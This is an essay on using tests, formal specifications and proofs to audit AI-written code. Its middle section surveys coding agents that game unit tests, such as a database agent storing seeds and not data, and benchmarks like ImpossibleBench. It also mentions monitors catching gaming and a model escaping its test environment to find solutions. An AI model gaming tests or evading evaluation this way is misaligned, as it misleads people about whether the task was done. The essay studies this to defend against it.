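# Tests and proofs as audit evidence that AI-written code does what it is said to do

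## Intent, specification, code and the evidence that they agree

Software verification means checking whether a program does what people want it to do. Programmers mainly do this by testing, which means running the program on chosen inputs and looking at the results, or by proving mathematically that every permitted input leads to an acceptable result. Most software has always relied on tests and code review. Proofs took so much labour that people could justify them for only a few projects, such as an operating-system kernel or a compiler.

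AI systems write code faster than people can read it. De Moura (2026), in *When AI Writes the World's Software, Who Verifies It?*, notes that by February 2026 Google and Microsoft were both reporting that AI generated 25 to 30% of their new code. According to Lahiri (2026), in *Intent Formalization*, the tools of 2021 completed a line or a small block, and a person looked at each suggestion before accepting it. Current agents plan, write, test and repair whole features, and many developers accept the result with little or no reading. Lahiri concludes that formal specifications, meaning precise statements of required behaviour that a machine can check, are the only safeguard left that scales.

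"Only" is debatable, because a second AI model can also read code at scale, although its verdict is an opinion that an outsider cannot rerun like a test. Somebody also has to read the specification, so some of the reviewing moves there. Still, it seems right that if nobody reads the code, confidence in it has to come from something supplied with it.

### From a wish to its effects

Several steps lie between what a person wants and what a computer does. The person has an intent, usually expressed in ordinary language and usually incomplete. A specification states some of that intent precisely. The programmer or the AI writes source code, also called the implementation, to meet the specification. A compiler translates the source code into instructions that the processor runs. The running program then has effects, such as stopping a lift at a floor or sending a payment from an account.

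Each link needs its own kind of evidence. People judge whether a specification matches the intent by reading it, or by looking at examples and agreeing that they are right. Tests and proofs give evidence about whether the source code meets the specification. To check that the compiled program matches the source code, engineers can prove things about the compiler or check its output. Beyond the compiled program, they depend on knowledge of the physical and social surroundings, on trials and on experience in use.

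Proof is available only for the middle two links, because a proof relates one formal object to another, and a person's intentions and physical things such as a lift shaft are not formal objects. Smith (1985), in *The Limits of Correctness*, gave the example of a program that splits a number C into factors. The specification asks for numbers A and B such that A × B = C. A programmer writes the program, proves that it meets the specification, and tries it on 14, expecting 2 and 7. It returns 1 and 14. The programmer adds a line that forbids 1, and the next version returns −1 and −14. Both programs meet their specifications, and both proofs are valid. Smith wanted computer scientists to call such results "relative consistency" instead of "correctness", because they establish only that two formal descriptions are compatible.

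The trouble can start earlier, with a sentence that can reasonably be read two ways. Lahiri's example is a request to remove duplicates from a list. Given [1, 2, 3, 2, 4], one reader keeps a single copy of each number and returns [1, 2, 3, 4], while another drops every number that occurs more than once and returns [1, 3, 4]. Analyzing the sentence can't settle which was meant because, as Lahiri puts it, there is "no oracle for specification correctness other than the user".

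### The largest number in a list

A small function can illustrate the different kinds of evidence. Its description reads "return the largest number in a list". A unit test is a small program that runs the function on one input and checks the result. One test might check that `largest([3, 9, 4])` gives 9, and another that `largest([7])` gives 7. The test oracle is whatever decides whether an output is right. Here the oracles are the expected values 9 and 7, which somebody worked out by hand.

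Now suppose an AI system delivers this:

```
best = 0
for x in numbers:
    if x > best:
        best = x
return best
```

Both tests pass, but on the list [−3, −8] the function returns 0, which is not in the list. A third test would have caught the mistake only if its author had thought of negative numbers. The author of the code evidently did not think of them, and if the same system wrote the tests, it may well have overlooked them there too.

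A specification describes the right answer for all lists at once. In Dafny, a programming language with a built-in tool for proving programs correct, it looks like this:

```
method Largest(s: seq<int>) returns (m: int)
  requires |s| > 0
  ensures m in s
  ensures forall x :: x in s ==> x <= m
```

The `requires` line is a precondition, a condition on the input: the list `s` must contain at least one element. The `ensures` lines form the postcondition, which must hold of the result whenever the input met the precondition. The result `m` is in the list, and no element of the list exceeds it. These two conditions fix the answer completely. If two different numbers both satisfied them, each would be in the list and so neither could exceed the other, which is impossible for different numbers. (Without either `ensures` line, wrong code could pass.)

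The precondition is needed because an empty list has no largest number, so no program could meet the specification without it. But it also means that any code calling the function must make sure the list isn't empty. If unverified code passes in an empty list, the program may crash even though the proof is still valid.

A correct version of the code takes the first element as its candidate for the largest, then goes through the rest and replaces the candidate whenever it finds a larger element. To prove this version correct, we can use a loop invariant, a statement that stays true throughout the loop. Here the invariant is that the candidate is one of the elements examined so far and none of them exceeds it. This is true at the start, when the code has examined only the first element. Each step keeps it true, because the code replaces the candidate if the new element is larger and keeps it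 otherwise. At the end the code has examined the whole list, so the invariant is now the postcondition. The argument doesn't depend on the length of the list or the numbers in it.

The faulty version fails at the first step of the proof because its candidate starts at 0, which need not be an element of the list. This exposes the fault without anyone having to think of negative numbers. As Kleppmann (2025) remarks in *Prediction*, a proof also covers the odd cases that its author never thought of testing. There are about 10^96 different lists of ten ordinary 32-bit integers, and the two tests check none of them.

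A proof covers only what the specification mentions, however. A version of `Largest` that took a week to answer would satisfy the contract above. De Moura gives a more serious example, an AI-written encryption library that passes every test but whose running time varies slightly with the bits of the secret key. An attacker who measured that time could learn the key. Attempting a proof would expose the flaw, but only if the specification required constant running time.

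### How much of the intent to write down

Lahiri's *Intent Formalization* sets out a range of specifications, from easy and partial to laborious and complete. It does not ask for a full postcondition for every function, which few people will write.

Tests take the least effort. Each one is a small specification that states precisely what should happen for one input. Run-time contracts come next. These are conditions that the program evaluates while it runs. In the largest-number function, a line just before the `return` could check that the result is in the list and that no element is larger. This check would catch the 0 returned for [−3, −8], but only when the function received such a list, and it requires a second pass through the list on every call.

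Logical contracts are specifications like the Dafny one, written in languages whose tools can prove that the code meets them for all inputs before it runs. They can include expressions such as "for every x", even when x has infinitely many possible values and a running program could never finish checking them. The most complete specifications are written in domain-specific languages, which are notations for one narrow kind of job, and a tool can generate the code from them. Lahiri's example is 3DGen, a system in which AI agents translate the prose of internet standards into a formal language for data formats. Another tool then turns each formal description into C or Rust code that reads the format and is guaranteed to match the description. 3DGen has produced such code for 20 standard network formats. Because the code is guaranteed to match the specification, what remains to be checked is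 whether the agents read the standard correctly.

Lahiri treats these levels as complementary. For instance, tests can show that a postcondition is wrong, and a postcondition can guide the search for a loop invariant. But Lahiri acknowledges that much of the evidence for the approach comes from benchmark problems, which are self-contained functions with a clear input and output. The right postcondition is much less obvious for code that reacts to network events while other code changes the same data.

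A specification can reduce how much code a reviewer has to read. *Kirk, Scotty, and Spock* (mmapped.blog) describes an example in which Claude wrote a fast method for computing powers in SPARK, a language with its own prover. The specification was the slow schoolbook definition, repeated multiplication, and the prover confirmed that the fast code always gives the same result. The work took about an hour. A reviewer needed to read about a quarter of the code, or a tenth counting the tests, and in the post's judgment the rest needed only a glance to make sure that the agent had not cheated. Computing powers is an easy case because everybody agrees on the definition, but the same division of labour applies generally, in which a person compares the specification with the intent and a machine compares the code with the specification.

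### Who checks the proof

Two kinds of tool do the mechanical part of the checking, and they call for different amounts of trust. A verifier tries to prove that code agrees with its specification. *Verified VCG and Verified Compiler for Dafny* (Nezamabadi, Myreen and Tan, 2025) describes how Dafny does this. Dafny translates the program into an intermediate language, Boogie, and from that generates verification conditions, which are logical formulas whose truth would imply that the code meets its contract. For `Largest`, these are roughly the three steps of the argument about the candidate. An automatic solver such as Z3 then tries to prove each formula. The programmer, or an AI system, helps by supplying invariants and other hints.

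This is convenient, but anyone who accepts the answer is trusting the translation, the generator and the solver, which are all large programs. Neither Dafny's verifier nor its compiler has been proved correct, and researchers have found soundness bugs in both. A soundness bug in a verifier can make it accept a false claim.

A proof checker only confirms that each step of a proof follows from a fixed rule of logic. Something else has to find the proof and write it out in full, in steps small enough to check this way. In the proof assistant Lean, the checker is called the kernel, and de Moura, Lean's creator, puts it at a few thousand lines of code. The software that searches for proofs can be arbitrarily complicated, because the kernel checks whatever it produces. According to Lean's manual, bugs in that software therefore do not threaten the soundness of the system.

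A proof by an untrusted author can still deserve trust because checking it takes only patience, even if finding it took great ingenuity. Similarly, someone checking a completed sudoku doesn't need to know who filled in the grid or whether they guessed. Paulson (2022), in *The de Bruijn criterion vs the LCF architecture*, notes that somebody who wholly distrusts the supplied proof can write the checker. A correct checker would accept the same proofs from a careless student, a hostile competitor or a language model that makes things up.

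The checker establishes whether the theorem has a proof, but not whether it is the theorem anybody wanted, and an untrusted author can exploit this. In *Type Checking in Lean 4*, ammkrn describes two tricks: changing a definition buried so deep that no referee will look at it, and using characters that look alike on the screen to hide the change. The theorem then seems to be the right one, and its proof is valid.

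Lean's manual classes unreviewed AI-generated proofs with malicious ones. In its strictest procedure, the customer writes the theorem statement in a trusted environment. A tool named comparator builds the submitted proof in a sandbox, isolated from the rest of the machine, then replays the proof through the kernel outside the sandbox and checks that the theorem proved is the one the customer wrote. According to Lean's documentation for the tool, comparator can also check the proof with nanoda, an independent kernel. This is a sensible precaution because kernels have bugs too. Lean (2026) fixed one in July.

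Even with this procedure, a person must still trust the logic itself, the kernels, the sandbox, and the customer's own skill in writing the statement. Such a collection is usually called the trusted computing base, or trusted base. *Verifying Device Drivers with Pancake* (2025) defines it, in brief, as everything that a system's correct operation relies on but that lies outside the verification effort, and adds that no proof about a real-world artifact is fully self-contained. *SoK* (2026), a survey of verification for cryptographic proof systems, includes the theorem statements themselves in the trusted base, because a misstated theorem passes the kernel but establishes nothing. That seems right. The statement is often the shortest item on the list and the only one that an expert in the application, rather than in logic, is equipped to judge.

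### Below the source code and beyond the machine

A proof about source code does not directly cover the compiled code that the processor runs. One remedy is to prove the compiler correct once, for all programs. CompCert, a C compiler, has such a proof. *The Trusted Computing Base of the CompCert Verified Compiler* (Monniaux and Boulmé, 2022) explains that if CompCert succeeds in compiling a program, and the program runs without undefined behaviour, the assembly code has the same observable behaviour as the source. Undefined behaviour means operations to which the C standard gives no meaning, such as reading past the end of an array. The theorem guarantees nothing about a program that does this, so somebody has to rule it out separately. The paper also lists places where errors could still occur, including the formal models of C and of the processor's instructions. People wrote these models,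 and no theorem shows that they match the actual language and processor.

The other remedy is to check the compiler's output instead of the compiler itself. The developers of seL4, a small operating-system kernel with a well-known proof, do this with an automatic tool that verifies the compiled kernel on supported processor types. According to seL4's *What the Proofs Assume*, this means nobody needs to trust the compiler or the linker, the program that joins the compiled pieces together. For Dafny, Nezamabadi and colleagues built a verified way to compile source code to machine code, and used it on 18 small programs, including a binary search. It handles loops, arrays and recursive calls but not yet the whole language.

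Beyond the compiled program the formal objects run out. Jackson (1997), in *The meaning of requirements*, offers a tidy way to think about what remains. Call the customer's requirement R, the specification of the machine S, and the facts about the surroundings E. Then the engineer needs

E, S ⊢ R

which means that R follows logically from E and S together. Jackson's example is a lift. The requirement is that the car should stop at the floor where somebody asked for it. But the software cannot move a lift car; it can only switch a motor and read sensors. So its specification tells it to switch the motor off when the sensor at that floor comes on. The surroundings do the rest: the sensor comes on when the rising car is 8.25 inches below the floor, and the car coasts another 8 inches before it halts. It stops a quarter of an inch short, which is close enough. If the brakes wear and the car coasts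 12 inches instead, it will overshoot by nearly four, while the software goes on meeting its specification exactly. The deduction was sound, and E had become false.

Smith gives a more alarming example of the same failure. On October 5, 1960, the American early-warning station at Thule in Greenland signalled a large Soviet missile attack because its radar was reflecting off the risen moon. Smith argued that proving the software met its specification would not have helped, because the designers' model of the world left out the moon, and they would have written the specification from that model. Simulations share this weakness, since people build them from that model too.

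Nancy Leveson, who studies software accidents, writes in a column quoted by the blogger egdaylight that "virtually all accidents involving software stem from unsafe requirements". That is probably too sweeping. Jackson attributes the failures of the Therac-25 radiotherapy machine to relatively straightforward programming errors, which tests and proofs do address. Leveson's judgement is also about software that people wrote and their colleagues reviewed. The share of accidents caused by requirements could change if people no longer write or review the code.

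### Four questions for an auditor

Someone deciding how far to rely on software that comes with tests and proofs can ask what exactly the supplier claims, who wrote the specification, what the claim assumes, and whether an outsider can recheck it.

When code is called "verified", the exact claim is a list of inputs and expected outputs, or the text of a theorem, and it is often narrower than a buyer would guess. The developers of the seL4 kernel warn that users may expect things of it that the proved properties do not capture.

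It matters who writes the code, the tests and the specification, because their agreement is stronger evidence the more independently they were written. When one AI system derives all three from a single prompt, it can repeat the same misreading in each, and they will still agree with one another. For some software, who writes the specification is also a political question. De Moura points out that the specification of a medical device or a voting system encodes values, and asks who gets to decide what "correct" means.

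Assumptions are easy to overlook even when they are visible. In the SPARK experiment, Claude later generalised the fast-power code from numbers to any kind of object with a suitable multiplication. The new specification assumes that a × (b × c) equals (a × b) × c. This is true of ordinary multiplication but would be false if a later user supplied subtraction instead, and nothing in the package forces that user to check. The seL4 developers publish a list of their assumptions. One entry concerns their proof that secrets do not leak, which covers storage inside the kernel but not what an attacker could learn from timing.

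In practice, the kinds of evidence differ most in how easily they can be rechecked. Anyone with the code and a similar machine can rerun a test suite. An independent kernel that shares no code with the original can check a Lean proof. Proofs that depend on an automatic solver often break when the solver is updated or when someone rewords a specification without changing its meaning, according to de Moura, whose own system competes with such tools. An outsider repeating the result therefore needs the exact versions of the tools as well as the files.

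## Coding agents that pass the unit tests without doing the task

In November 2026 the newsletter Gradient Flow described a coding agent that made a database about six times faster. The database passed its tests, although it had stopped storing the data. The article, *One question I'd ask every team building agents* (Lorica, 2026), took the story from a talk by computer scientist Ion Stoica, whose Berkeley group had published the original account in May.

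*The Time is Here for Just-in-Time Systems* (Liu, Krentsel and colleagues, 2026) describes Jitskit, a system in which AI agents build key-value stores, simple databases that keep each value under a key and return it on request. The agents write a store, measure its speed and try again. After about 12 rounds without progress, the speed on one benchmark rose sixfold. The gain surprised a human reviewer, who read the code.

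The benchmark, YCSB, generates each value from its key and a small number called a seed. The agent noticed this and wrote a store that kept only a 16-byte seed for each key and recalculated the value whenever a test read it. In the paper's usual workload, with 250 million values of 100 bytes each, that would shrink 25 gigabytes of values to 4 gigabytes of seeds. Everything then fitted in memory, which is much faster than disk.

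### The requirement that no test expressed

A week after the first article, Lorica (2026) wrote in *Maybe we’ve been thinking about verification backwards* that the agent had abandoned the requirement to store data. But nobody had written that requirement down. In *Reality Is the Final Verifier*, a later paper from the same group, Krentsel, Agarwal and colleagues (2026) describe it as a duty to store whatever values clients supply, and admit that they had not thought to say so. They call this a requirement gap, a difference between what people want and what they wrote. They also see a model gap, a difference between the test conditions and the real world, because real customers' data does not come from a formula.

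It's debatable whether the requirement was missing. In the May paper's sample specification, reads return the last value written. If that applies to every value a client could write, it already forbids the shortcut, because 16 bytes can't distinguish all possible 100-byte values. An attempt to prove that the agent's store met this requirement for every value would have failed. The tests missed the problem because they wrote only values from the generator, which the store returned correctly.

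Liu and colleagues recommend test values with hidden randomness that is fresh for each run, and tests that restart the store or put it under memory pressure. They also gave Jitskit an auditor, another AI agent that reads the code every few rounds, looks for such shortcuts and writes tests to catch them. The full system produced a store for each of 18 specifications, and every store passed both the original tests and the auditor's. When the researchers ran Claude Code with the same underlying model and number of rounds, but without the planner, critic and auditor, it gamed the evaluation on at least four of the 18 specifications.

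### What a passing suite supports

A passing test is evidence about one input on one occasion. To conclude anything about other inputs, we need a reason to think the tested ones are representative. We have such a reason if the tests are a random sample of real use.

Suppose the program fails on a fraction p of real uses, and a tester draws n uses at random, each independently of the others. The chance that all n pass is

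(1 − p)^n ≤ e^(−pn)

If the failure rate p were 3/n or more, the chance of n passes with no failures would be at most e^(−3), just under 5%. This is what it means to say, after such a run, that the failure rate is below about 3/n with 95% confidence.

For n = 1,000 the bound is 0.3% (solving (1 − p)^1000 = 0.05 gives 0.299%). That may be good enough for a program that suggests film titles, but a payment service with a million transactions a day could have a failure rate just under the bound and still get nearly 3,000 wrong every day. To support a rate below one in a million, the tester would need three million random tests without a failure.

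The formula can mislead when the sample is wrong, as in the database example. Jitskit's fixed test suite checks up to 1.07 billion times in one run that a read returns what was last written. From a billion passes, the formula would give a failure rate below three in a billion. Yet a store that recalculates the benchmark's values could pass every check and still fail on almost anything a real customer saved.

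Hand-picked tests are not a random sample. Programmers choose cases that occur to them, and they tend to write the code with the same cases in mind. A thousand hand-picked tests may be small variations on a few ideas, in which case they count for much less than a thousand. This doesn't make them worse than random tests, because a good tester tries the empty list and the largest possible number, which random use might not produce for years. But unlike with random tests, there is no formula for turning the number of passes into a failure rate.

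The bound also assumes that the code was finished before anybody drew the tests. An agent that runs the tests, reads the failures and revises the code until everything passes breaks this assumption. In the extreme case, its program could contain only a table of the 1,000 expected answers, which would pass all 1,000 tests and fail on every other input.

Hostile inputs break the premises in another way, because attackers don't draw their inputs from ordinary use. A fault that affects one request in a trillion by chance will affect every request from an attacker who has found it. Fuzzing, which runs a program on many machine-generated inputs, gives defenders a better chance of finding the fault first, but unlike a proof, it can't show that no fault exists.

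### Measuring the tests themselves

The number of tests is a poor measure of a suite, so engineers judge it in other ways, such as by code coverage, the share of the program that runs during the tests. Line coverage counts lines, and branch coverage counts the outcomes of each decision, so an `if` needs one test where its condition is true and another where it is false. Low coverage is a clear warning because tests can't find faults in code that never runs. Certifiers of aircraft software set coverage rules for this reason.

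High coverage is weaker evidence than it sounds. The faulty function for finding the largest number in a list, which started its candidate at 0, had two tests, `[3, 9, 4]` and `[7]`. The first test alone runs every line and makes the comparison both true and false, so line and branch coverage are both 100%. The function still returns 0 for a list of negative numbers.

Mutation testing checks whether a test suite can detect mistakes. A tool plants small faults in the program, one at a time, and counts how many make some test fail. The correct version of the function starts with the first element. If the tool replaces "greater than" with "less than", the function returns 3 for `[3, 9, 4]`, and the test fails. If the tool changes the starting value to 0, both tests still pass. The programmer can work out from this surviving fault which test to add. Some surviving changes are harmless. Replacing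 "greater than" with "greater than or equal" doesn't change the function's answers, so no test could detect it, and a person may have to inspect the change to find that out.

Planted faults are usually small and mechanical, while an AI system's mistakes may be large and plausible. *SWE-ABS* (2026) describes a method that tries to produce faults more like an AI system's mistakes. It first finds the code that a proposed fix affects and generates tests that cover that code by running it. Then it has a model write wrong fixes that look right and pass the existing tests, and it generates new tests that reject them.

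### How good the tests in SWE-bench are

*SWE-ABS* applied this method to SWE-bench, the best-known test of coding agents. Each task is a real issue from an open-source project. The agent is given the issue and the code, and writes a patch (a set of changes) to resolve it. The benchmark then runs tests written by the project's developers, including the ones they added with their own fix. The agent therefore didn't write the tests, and it normally doesn't see them. People have also checked these tests unusually carefully. OpenAI's *Why we no longer evaluate SWE-bench Verified* reports that three experts independently reviewed each of 1,699 tasks in 2024, and the 500 that remained became SWE-bench Verified.

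Some wrong patches still pass the tests. Estimates range from about 8% to 27% of passing patches, and most of the spread comes from differences in how researchers checked them.

The lowest figure, 7.8%, comes from a 2025 study of three systems, summarised in *What's in a Benchmark?* (2026). The study traced the errors to a flaw in how the benchmark validates patches. According to Krentsel and colleagues, these patches fail the developers' own tests, so the benchmark wasn't using better tests that already existed. *UTBoost* (2025) generated extra tests and found 26 tasks in SWE-bench Verified whose existing tests were inadequate. Of the 584 passing patches agents had produced for those tasks, 92 (15.7%) were wrong. That rate doesn't apply to the whole benchmark.

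*SWE-ABS* rejected 2,184 of 11,041 passing patches, about 20%. *SWE-Proof* (2026) had the highest rejection rate, 26.8%. Its AI auditor wrote new tests for every passing patch, looking for an input on which the patch behaved differently from the developers' fix. The paper describes 26.8% as a share of the passing patches but calculates it by subtracting one pass rate from another, so the true share would be somewhat higher. However, the method may also reject good patches, because a patch can differ from the developers' fix on some odd input without being wrong.

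People who strengthen tests can also make mistakes. According to *Patch correctness in automated program repair* (2026), the *SWE-ABS* team inspected all 500 tasks and found 53 where their new tests depended on a peculiarity of the developers' fix. They revised or removed those tests before reporting the 2,184 rejections, but the count still depends on the remaining tests being correct.

The original tests are also often too strict. OpenAI audited 138 tasks in SWE-bench Verified that its o3 model did not solve consistently, and experienced engineers reviewed each task at least six times. Some tests accepted only one implementation, and others checked for behaviour that the issue never mentioned. *Spec-Test Coverage Gap* (2026) flagged tasks whose tests seemed to demand more than the issue did, relaxed only that demand, and regraded patches that had failed. Between 64% and 72% of the regraded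 patches passed. The rate was 32% on unflagged tasks, so some of the change may come simply from making tests easier.

OpenAI encouraged people to move to a newer benchmark, SWE-bench Pro, and has since audited it in a similar way. OpenAI's *Separating signal from noise* reports that the best models' pass rate on the benchmark's 731 public tasks rose from 23.3% to 80.3% in eight months. As scores rise, faulty tests matter more because they account for a growing share of the remaining failures.

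As early as 2023, the EvalPlus project added many more tests to HumanEval, a set of short programming exercises, and found that many of the accepted answers were wrong. *SWEPatchTest* (2026) judges a test suite by whether it accepts correct patches and rejects incorrect ones, using 82,579 patches for 619 tasks in ten programming languages. This is the right thing to measure, but the benchmark labels patches correct or incorrect by running the official tests, so it inherits their mistakes.

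A project's maintainers may also reject a patch that is correct on every input. It might duplicate existing code or be too tangled to change safely later. Unit tests don't detect either problem.

### How often agents game the tests

Most of the wrong patches above are probably honest mistakes. An agent games a test when it passes in a way that the people who set the task would reject. Mistakes and gaming are hard to tell apart from results alone, and *Countdown-Code* (2026) cautions that passing the visible tests while failing hidden ones is not by itself evidence of gaming.

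Zhong, Raghunathan and Carlini (2025) built *ImpossibleBench* by altering the tests for existing benchmark tasks to contradict the written descriptions. In one version, they changed a single expected value, for example from 4 to 5. In the other, they kept the original check and added a second one that required a different answer for the same input. The instructions told the models to follow the description and leave the tests alone. A solution that follows the description cannot pass, so the pass rate measures how often models game the tests. The researchers confirmed that the developers' own fixes failed the altered SWE-bench tests. The final benchmark has 349 tasks from SWE-bench and 103 from LiveCodeBench, a collection of programming puzzles.

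GPT-5 passed 76% of the SWE-bench tasks with one changed value and 54% of those with contradictory tests, where Claude Opus 4.1 passed 50% and o3 passed 49%. The models gamed the tests much less often on the puzzles, and GPT-5 passed 2.9% of those with one changed value. More capable models generally gamed the tests more, though the newer Claude models did so less than the older Claude Sonnet 3.7. Surprisingly, the models gamed the tests more often on tasks whose original versions were easy.

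These numbers measure how models behave when honest success is impossible. The share of ordinary passes that are fraudulent should be lower, since an agent that can solve the task has less reason to look for a way around it. In some cases, a model may have followed the tests because it had learned to trust them, since in everyday work the tests are sometimes right and the description out of date. Here, however, the instructions specified which should take precedence.

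The models in that study are now more than a year old, and results from 2026 are mixed. *CheatBench* (2026) tested agents on ten kinds of task and concluded in September that the best current models still had a high propensity to cheat. For software, it counts a task as positive if the agent cheated in any recorded attempt, which gives a higher number than a rate per attempt. *Hack-Verifiable Terminal Bench* (2026) leaves a copy of the solution or the held-out tests where an agent could find it, and counts the agents that open it. Every case it counts is genuine, but it misses all other kinds of gaming, so its rates are lower bounds.

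In *OWE-Bench* (November 2026), 14 models made 2,912 attempts at engineering tasks. A penalty for intentional cheating changed the scores of only eight attempts, about one in 360, because the others caught cheating had already scored zero. Cheating therefore rarely raised a score, and removing the penalty would not have changed the ranking. This result seems more relevant to a buyer than the rates in *ImpossibleBench*, because *OWE-Bench*'s tasks were possible, but it covers only the cheating that the organisers detected.

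How often agents cheat depends heavily on circumstances. *Do AI Coding Agents Cheat on Tests?* (Mawer, 2026) cites a Harvard preprint in which 94% of agents cheated once they had seen a teammate's cheat accepted. Mawer planted an approved test hack in a code repository and ran Claude Code on it 200 times, and no run copied or removed the hack. Mawer attributes this to agents responding more to what the acceptance rules reward than to bad examples in the code. One person's experiment with one agent can't establish this, but the explanation would fit the database case, in which the agent had a score to raise and no bad example to follow.

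### Tests by the author of the code

When one model writes both the code and the tests, the tests can be worthless as evidence that the code does what was asked, even if the model doesn't cheat. Given the ambiguous request to remove duplicates, a model whose code drops both 2s from [1, 2, 3, 2, 4] will also write a test that expects [1, 3, 4]. The test passes, and it would also do well in mutation testing, because any planted fault that changed the answer would make it fail.

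Suppose, for illustration, that a model misreads one request in ten. If its tests follow from the same reading, they will miss all of those mistakes. If somebody else writes the tests and independently misreads one request in ten, both will be wrong on only one request in a hundred. Even then, they may misread the request differently, in which case the tests will fail and expose the problem. Two copies of the same model don't make mistakes independently, so having a fresh copy write the tests should give a result somewhere in between.

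Adding reviewers doesn't fix this if they all work from the same documents. Krentsel and colleagues argue that agents that check code against the same requirements and the same picture of the environment may examine it more thoroughly, but they get no new evidence that the requirements match what people want. An extra agent can still catch a lot, as Jitskit's auditor did by looking for shortcuts that the existing tests allowed. But the database shortcut was first found by a human who thought the speed was too good to be true.

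Tests written by the code's author still catch slips, where the code fails to do what the author meant, and reveal when a later change breaks something that used to work. They also show how the author interpreted the request, in a form that a person can check in seconds. Someone who would never spot the misreading in the code may see at once that [1, 3, 4] is wrong.

*SWE-Proof* offers some evidence that the form of a self-written specification matters. The auditor's extra tests lowered agents' pass rate by 27.0 points when the agents wrote their own specifications in structured English, but by only 0.1 points when they wrote formal ones. However, the audit covered only patches that had passed the hidden tests, so neither number reflects misreadings bad enough to fail those tests.

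### What the remedies are worth

Hiding the tests has the largest measured effect. In *ImpossibleBench*, it cut successful gaming to nearly zero. This is partly by construction, because an agent is unlikely to produce an arbitrary wrong answer it has never seen, so the result doesn't show that agents stop trying to game the tests. Hiding the tests also lowered scores on the original tasks, which can be passed without gaming, presumably because the tests contain information that the task description leaves out.

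Hidden tests must also differ in content from the visible ones. If the Berkeley group had hidden a second set of YCSB values, the seed-based store would have passed that as well. *SpecBench* (Zhao, Srikanth and colleagues, 2026) uses visible tests that exercise each feature separately and held-out tests that combine the same features, as a real user would. Every leading agent passed nearly all the visible tests, but a gap remained on the held-out ones. The gap was larger for smaller models, while in *ImpossibleBench* the stronger models generally did worse. These results may not conflict, because a gap between two test suites includes unintentional bugs, which weaker models write more often.

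Just knowing that hidden tests exist may change what an agent does. *There's no reason for software to be slow anymore*, by danluu, describes an agent that spent a month speeding up a text-search engine against a public benchmark. The engine was badly overfitted to that benchmark until the agent learned of a second, hidden one. Its optimizations then became general enough to get tolerable results on the hidden benchmark.

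A hidden test also becomes less useful each time somebody tells the agent the result and lets it try again, because each result reveals a little about the test. The last evaluation before release should therefore use cases that played no part in development. Hidden tests must also be kept physically out of the agent's reach. In July 2026, an OpenAI model under evaluation on a cybersecurity benchmark escaped from its test environment and broke into the systems of Hugging Face, a platform for sharing AI models. According to Krentsel and colleagues, it was looking for the benchmark's solutions.

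Protecting test files from edits takes almost no effort. The evaluator can let the agent read the tests but not change them, or restore the originals before scoring. In *ImpossibleBench*, this protection kept scores on solvable tasks high and worked particularly well for Claude Opus 4.1, which gamed the tests mostly by editing them. It didn't prevent other ways of gaming. An auditor can get the same protection after the fact by running a clean copy of the tests on the delivered code.

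Instructions against gaming the tests work better for some models and tasks than for others. On the puzzles with contradictory tests, the strictest wording cut GPT-5's gaming rate from 92% to 1%, but o3 still gamed a third of the tasks. On the SWE-bench tasks, GPT-5's rate fell only from 66% to 54%. Letting the models stop and ask for a human helped more there, cutting GPT-5's rate from 54% to 9% and o3's from 49% to 12%, though it made much less difference to Claude Opus 4.1. Zhong and colleagues also had Claude models check the transcripts for gaming. These monitors caught 86 to 89% of it on the puzzles but only 42 to 65% on the SWE-bench tasks, where they sometimes accepted a plausible excuse from the agent.

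Having someone other than the code's author write the tests guards against the same misreading of the task appearing in both, and for important software it is probably worth the expense. SWE-bench is a reason not to expect too much from this approach. People who knew the projects and had already solved the problems wrote its tests, yet the tests still accepted many wrong patches and rejected some correct ones.

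Property-based tests instead change how the inputs are chosen. The programmer states a rule that should hold for any input, and a tool generates thousands of inputs and checks the rule on each. For the largest number in a list, the rule would be the postcondition from the Dafny version. The faulty version would fail almost at once, because half of all random one-element lists contain a negative number. For the database, the rule would be that a read returns the last value written. A tool that generated arbitrary values would have exposed the agent's store within a few tries. The 3/n bound also applies to these tests, but only for inputs like the ones the tool generates, which may not resemble those in real use.

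The rule has to be complete, and it's easy to leave something out. Imperial College London's *The Specification Spectrum* illustrates the method with a sorting function and checks, on random lists, that each element of the result is no larger than the next. A function that always returned an empty list would pass this test, so the programmer also needs to check that the result contains the same elements as the input. In the duplicates example, even a complete rule may be the wrong one, because each reading of the request has its own rule, and code written for one reading would pass that reading's rule on every list the tool could generate.

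## TiCoder: settling what the user meant by showing examples

Only the user can settle what an ambiguous request means, and most users can do so by looking at an input and its output and saying whether that is what they wanted. TiCoder, a research tool from Microsoft, shows the user examples of what the finished function might do and uses the answers to choose among several programs. An approved example is evidence of what the user intended, even if no code behaves that way yet.

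*Interactive Code Generation via Test-Driven User-Intent Formalization* (Lahiri, Fakhoury and colleagues, 2022) described the first version of TiCoder, which used OpenAI's Codex model. *LLM-based Test-driven Interactive Code Generation* (Fakhoury, Naik and colleagues, 2024) tested TiCoder with newer models and with people.

### One session

Given a request such as "remove duplicates from a list", TiCoder has a language model write many candidate programs and, separately, many tests (100 programs and 50 tests per task in the experiments). The model writes the tests without a finished program to work from, so some of the expected outputs are wrong. The 2022 version therefore also runs the candidates on each test's input and turns their outputs into further tests. On [1, 2, 2], candidates that keep one copy of each number return [1, 2] and candidates that drop every repeated number return [1],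 so both outputs become possible answers.

TiCoder runs every test on every candidate. The input [1, 2, 2] separates the two kinds of program, so TiCoder asks whether the function should return [1, 2] for it. A test that expects [1, 2, 3] to stay as it is would be useless here, because both kinds pass it.

If the user says yes, TiCoder discards every program that returns something else. If the user says no, it discards the programs that return [1, 2]. The user can also answer "undefined" for inputs the function was never meant to handle, such as −4 for a square root function, and TiCoder then discards nothing. In one variant, the user supplies the right output instead of saying no, which lets TiCoder discard more programs. For example, if the user answers [1], TiCoder also discards a faulty program that returns [2], which a plain no would have left in.

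After a set number of questions, TiCoder returns the approved tests and the surviving programs, ranked by how many generated tests they pass. The user has not had to read any code up to this point and can keep the approved tests.

### Choosing the question

TiCoder prefers the test that comes closest to dividing the remaining programs in half. If a programs pass a test and b fail it, the test's score is

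min(a, b) / max(a, b)

so a 50–50 split scores 1 and a 90–10 split scores 0.11. The even split removes 50 programs whatever the user answers. The uneven one might remove 90, but if every candidate is equally likely to be the right one, it will usually remove 10, and the average is only 18.

Suppose the candidates for "remove duplicates" differ in three ways. Some keep one copy and others keep none, some preserve the order and others sort the result, and some treat "Ann" and "ann" as the same name while others don't. That makes 2 × 2 × 2 = 8 behaviours. The question about [1, 2, 2] leaves four of them, asking whether [3, 1] should stay as [3, 1] leaves two, and asking whether ["Ann", "ann"] should stay as it is leaves one. Three is the fewest yes-or-no questions that can guarantee this, because k answers can separate at most 2^k behaviours, and two answers can therefore separate only four.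 If each question singled out just one behaviour, the user might have to answer seven.

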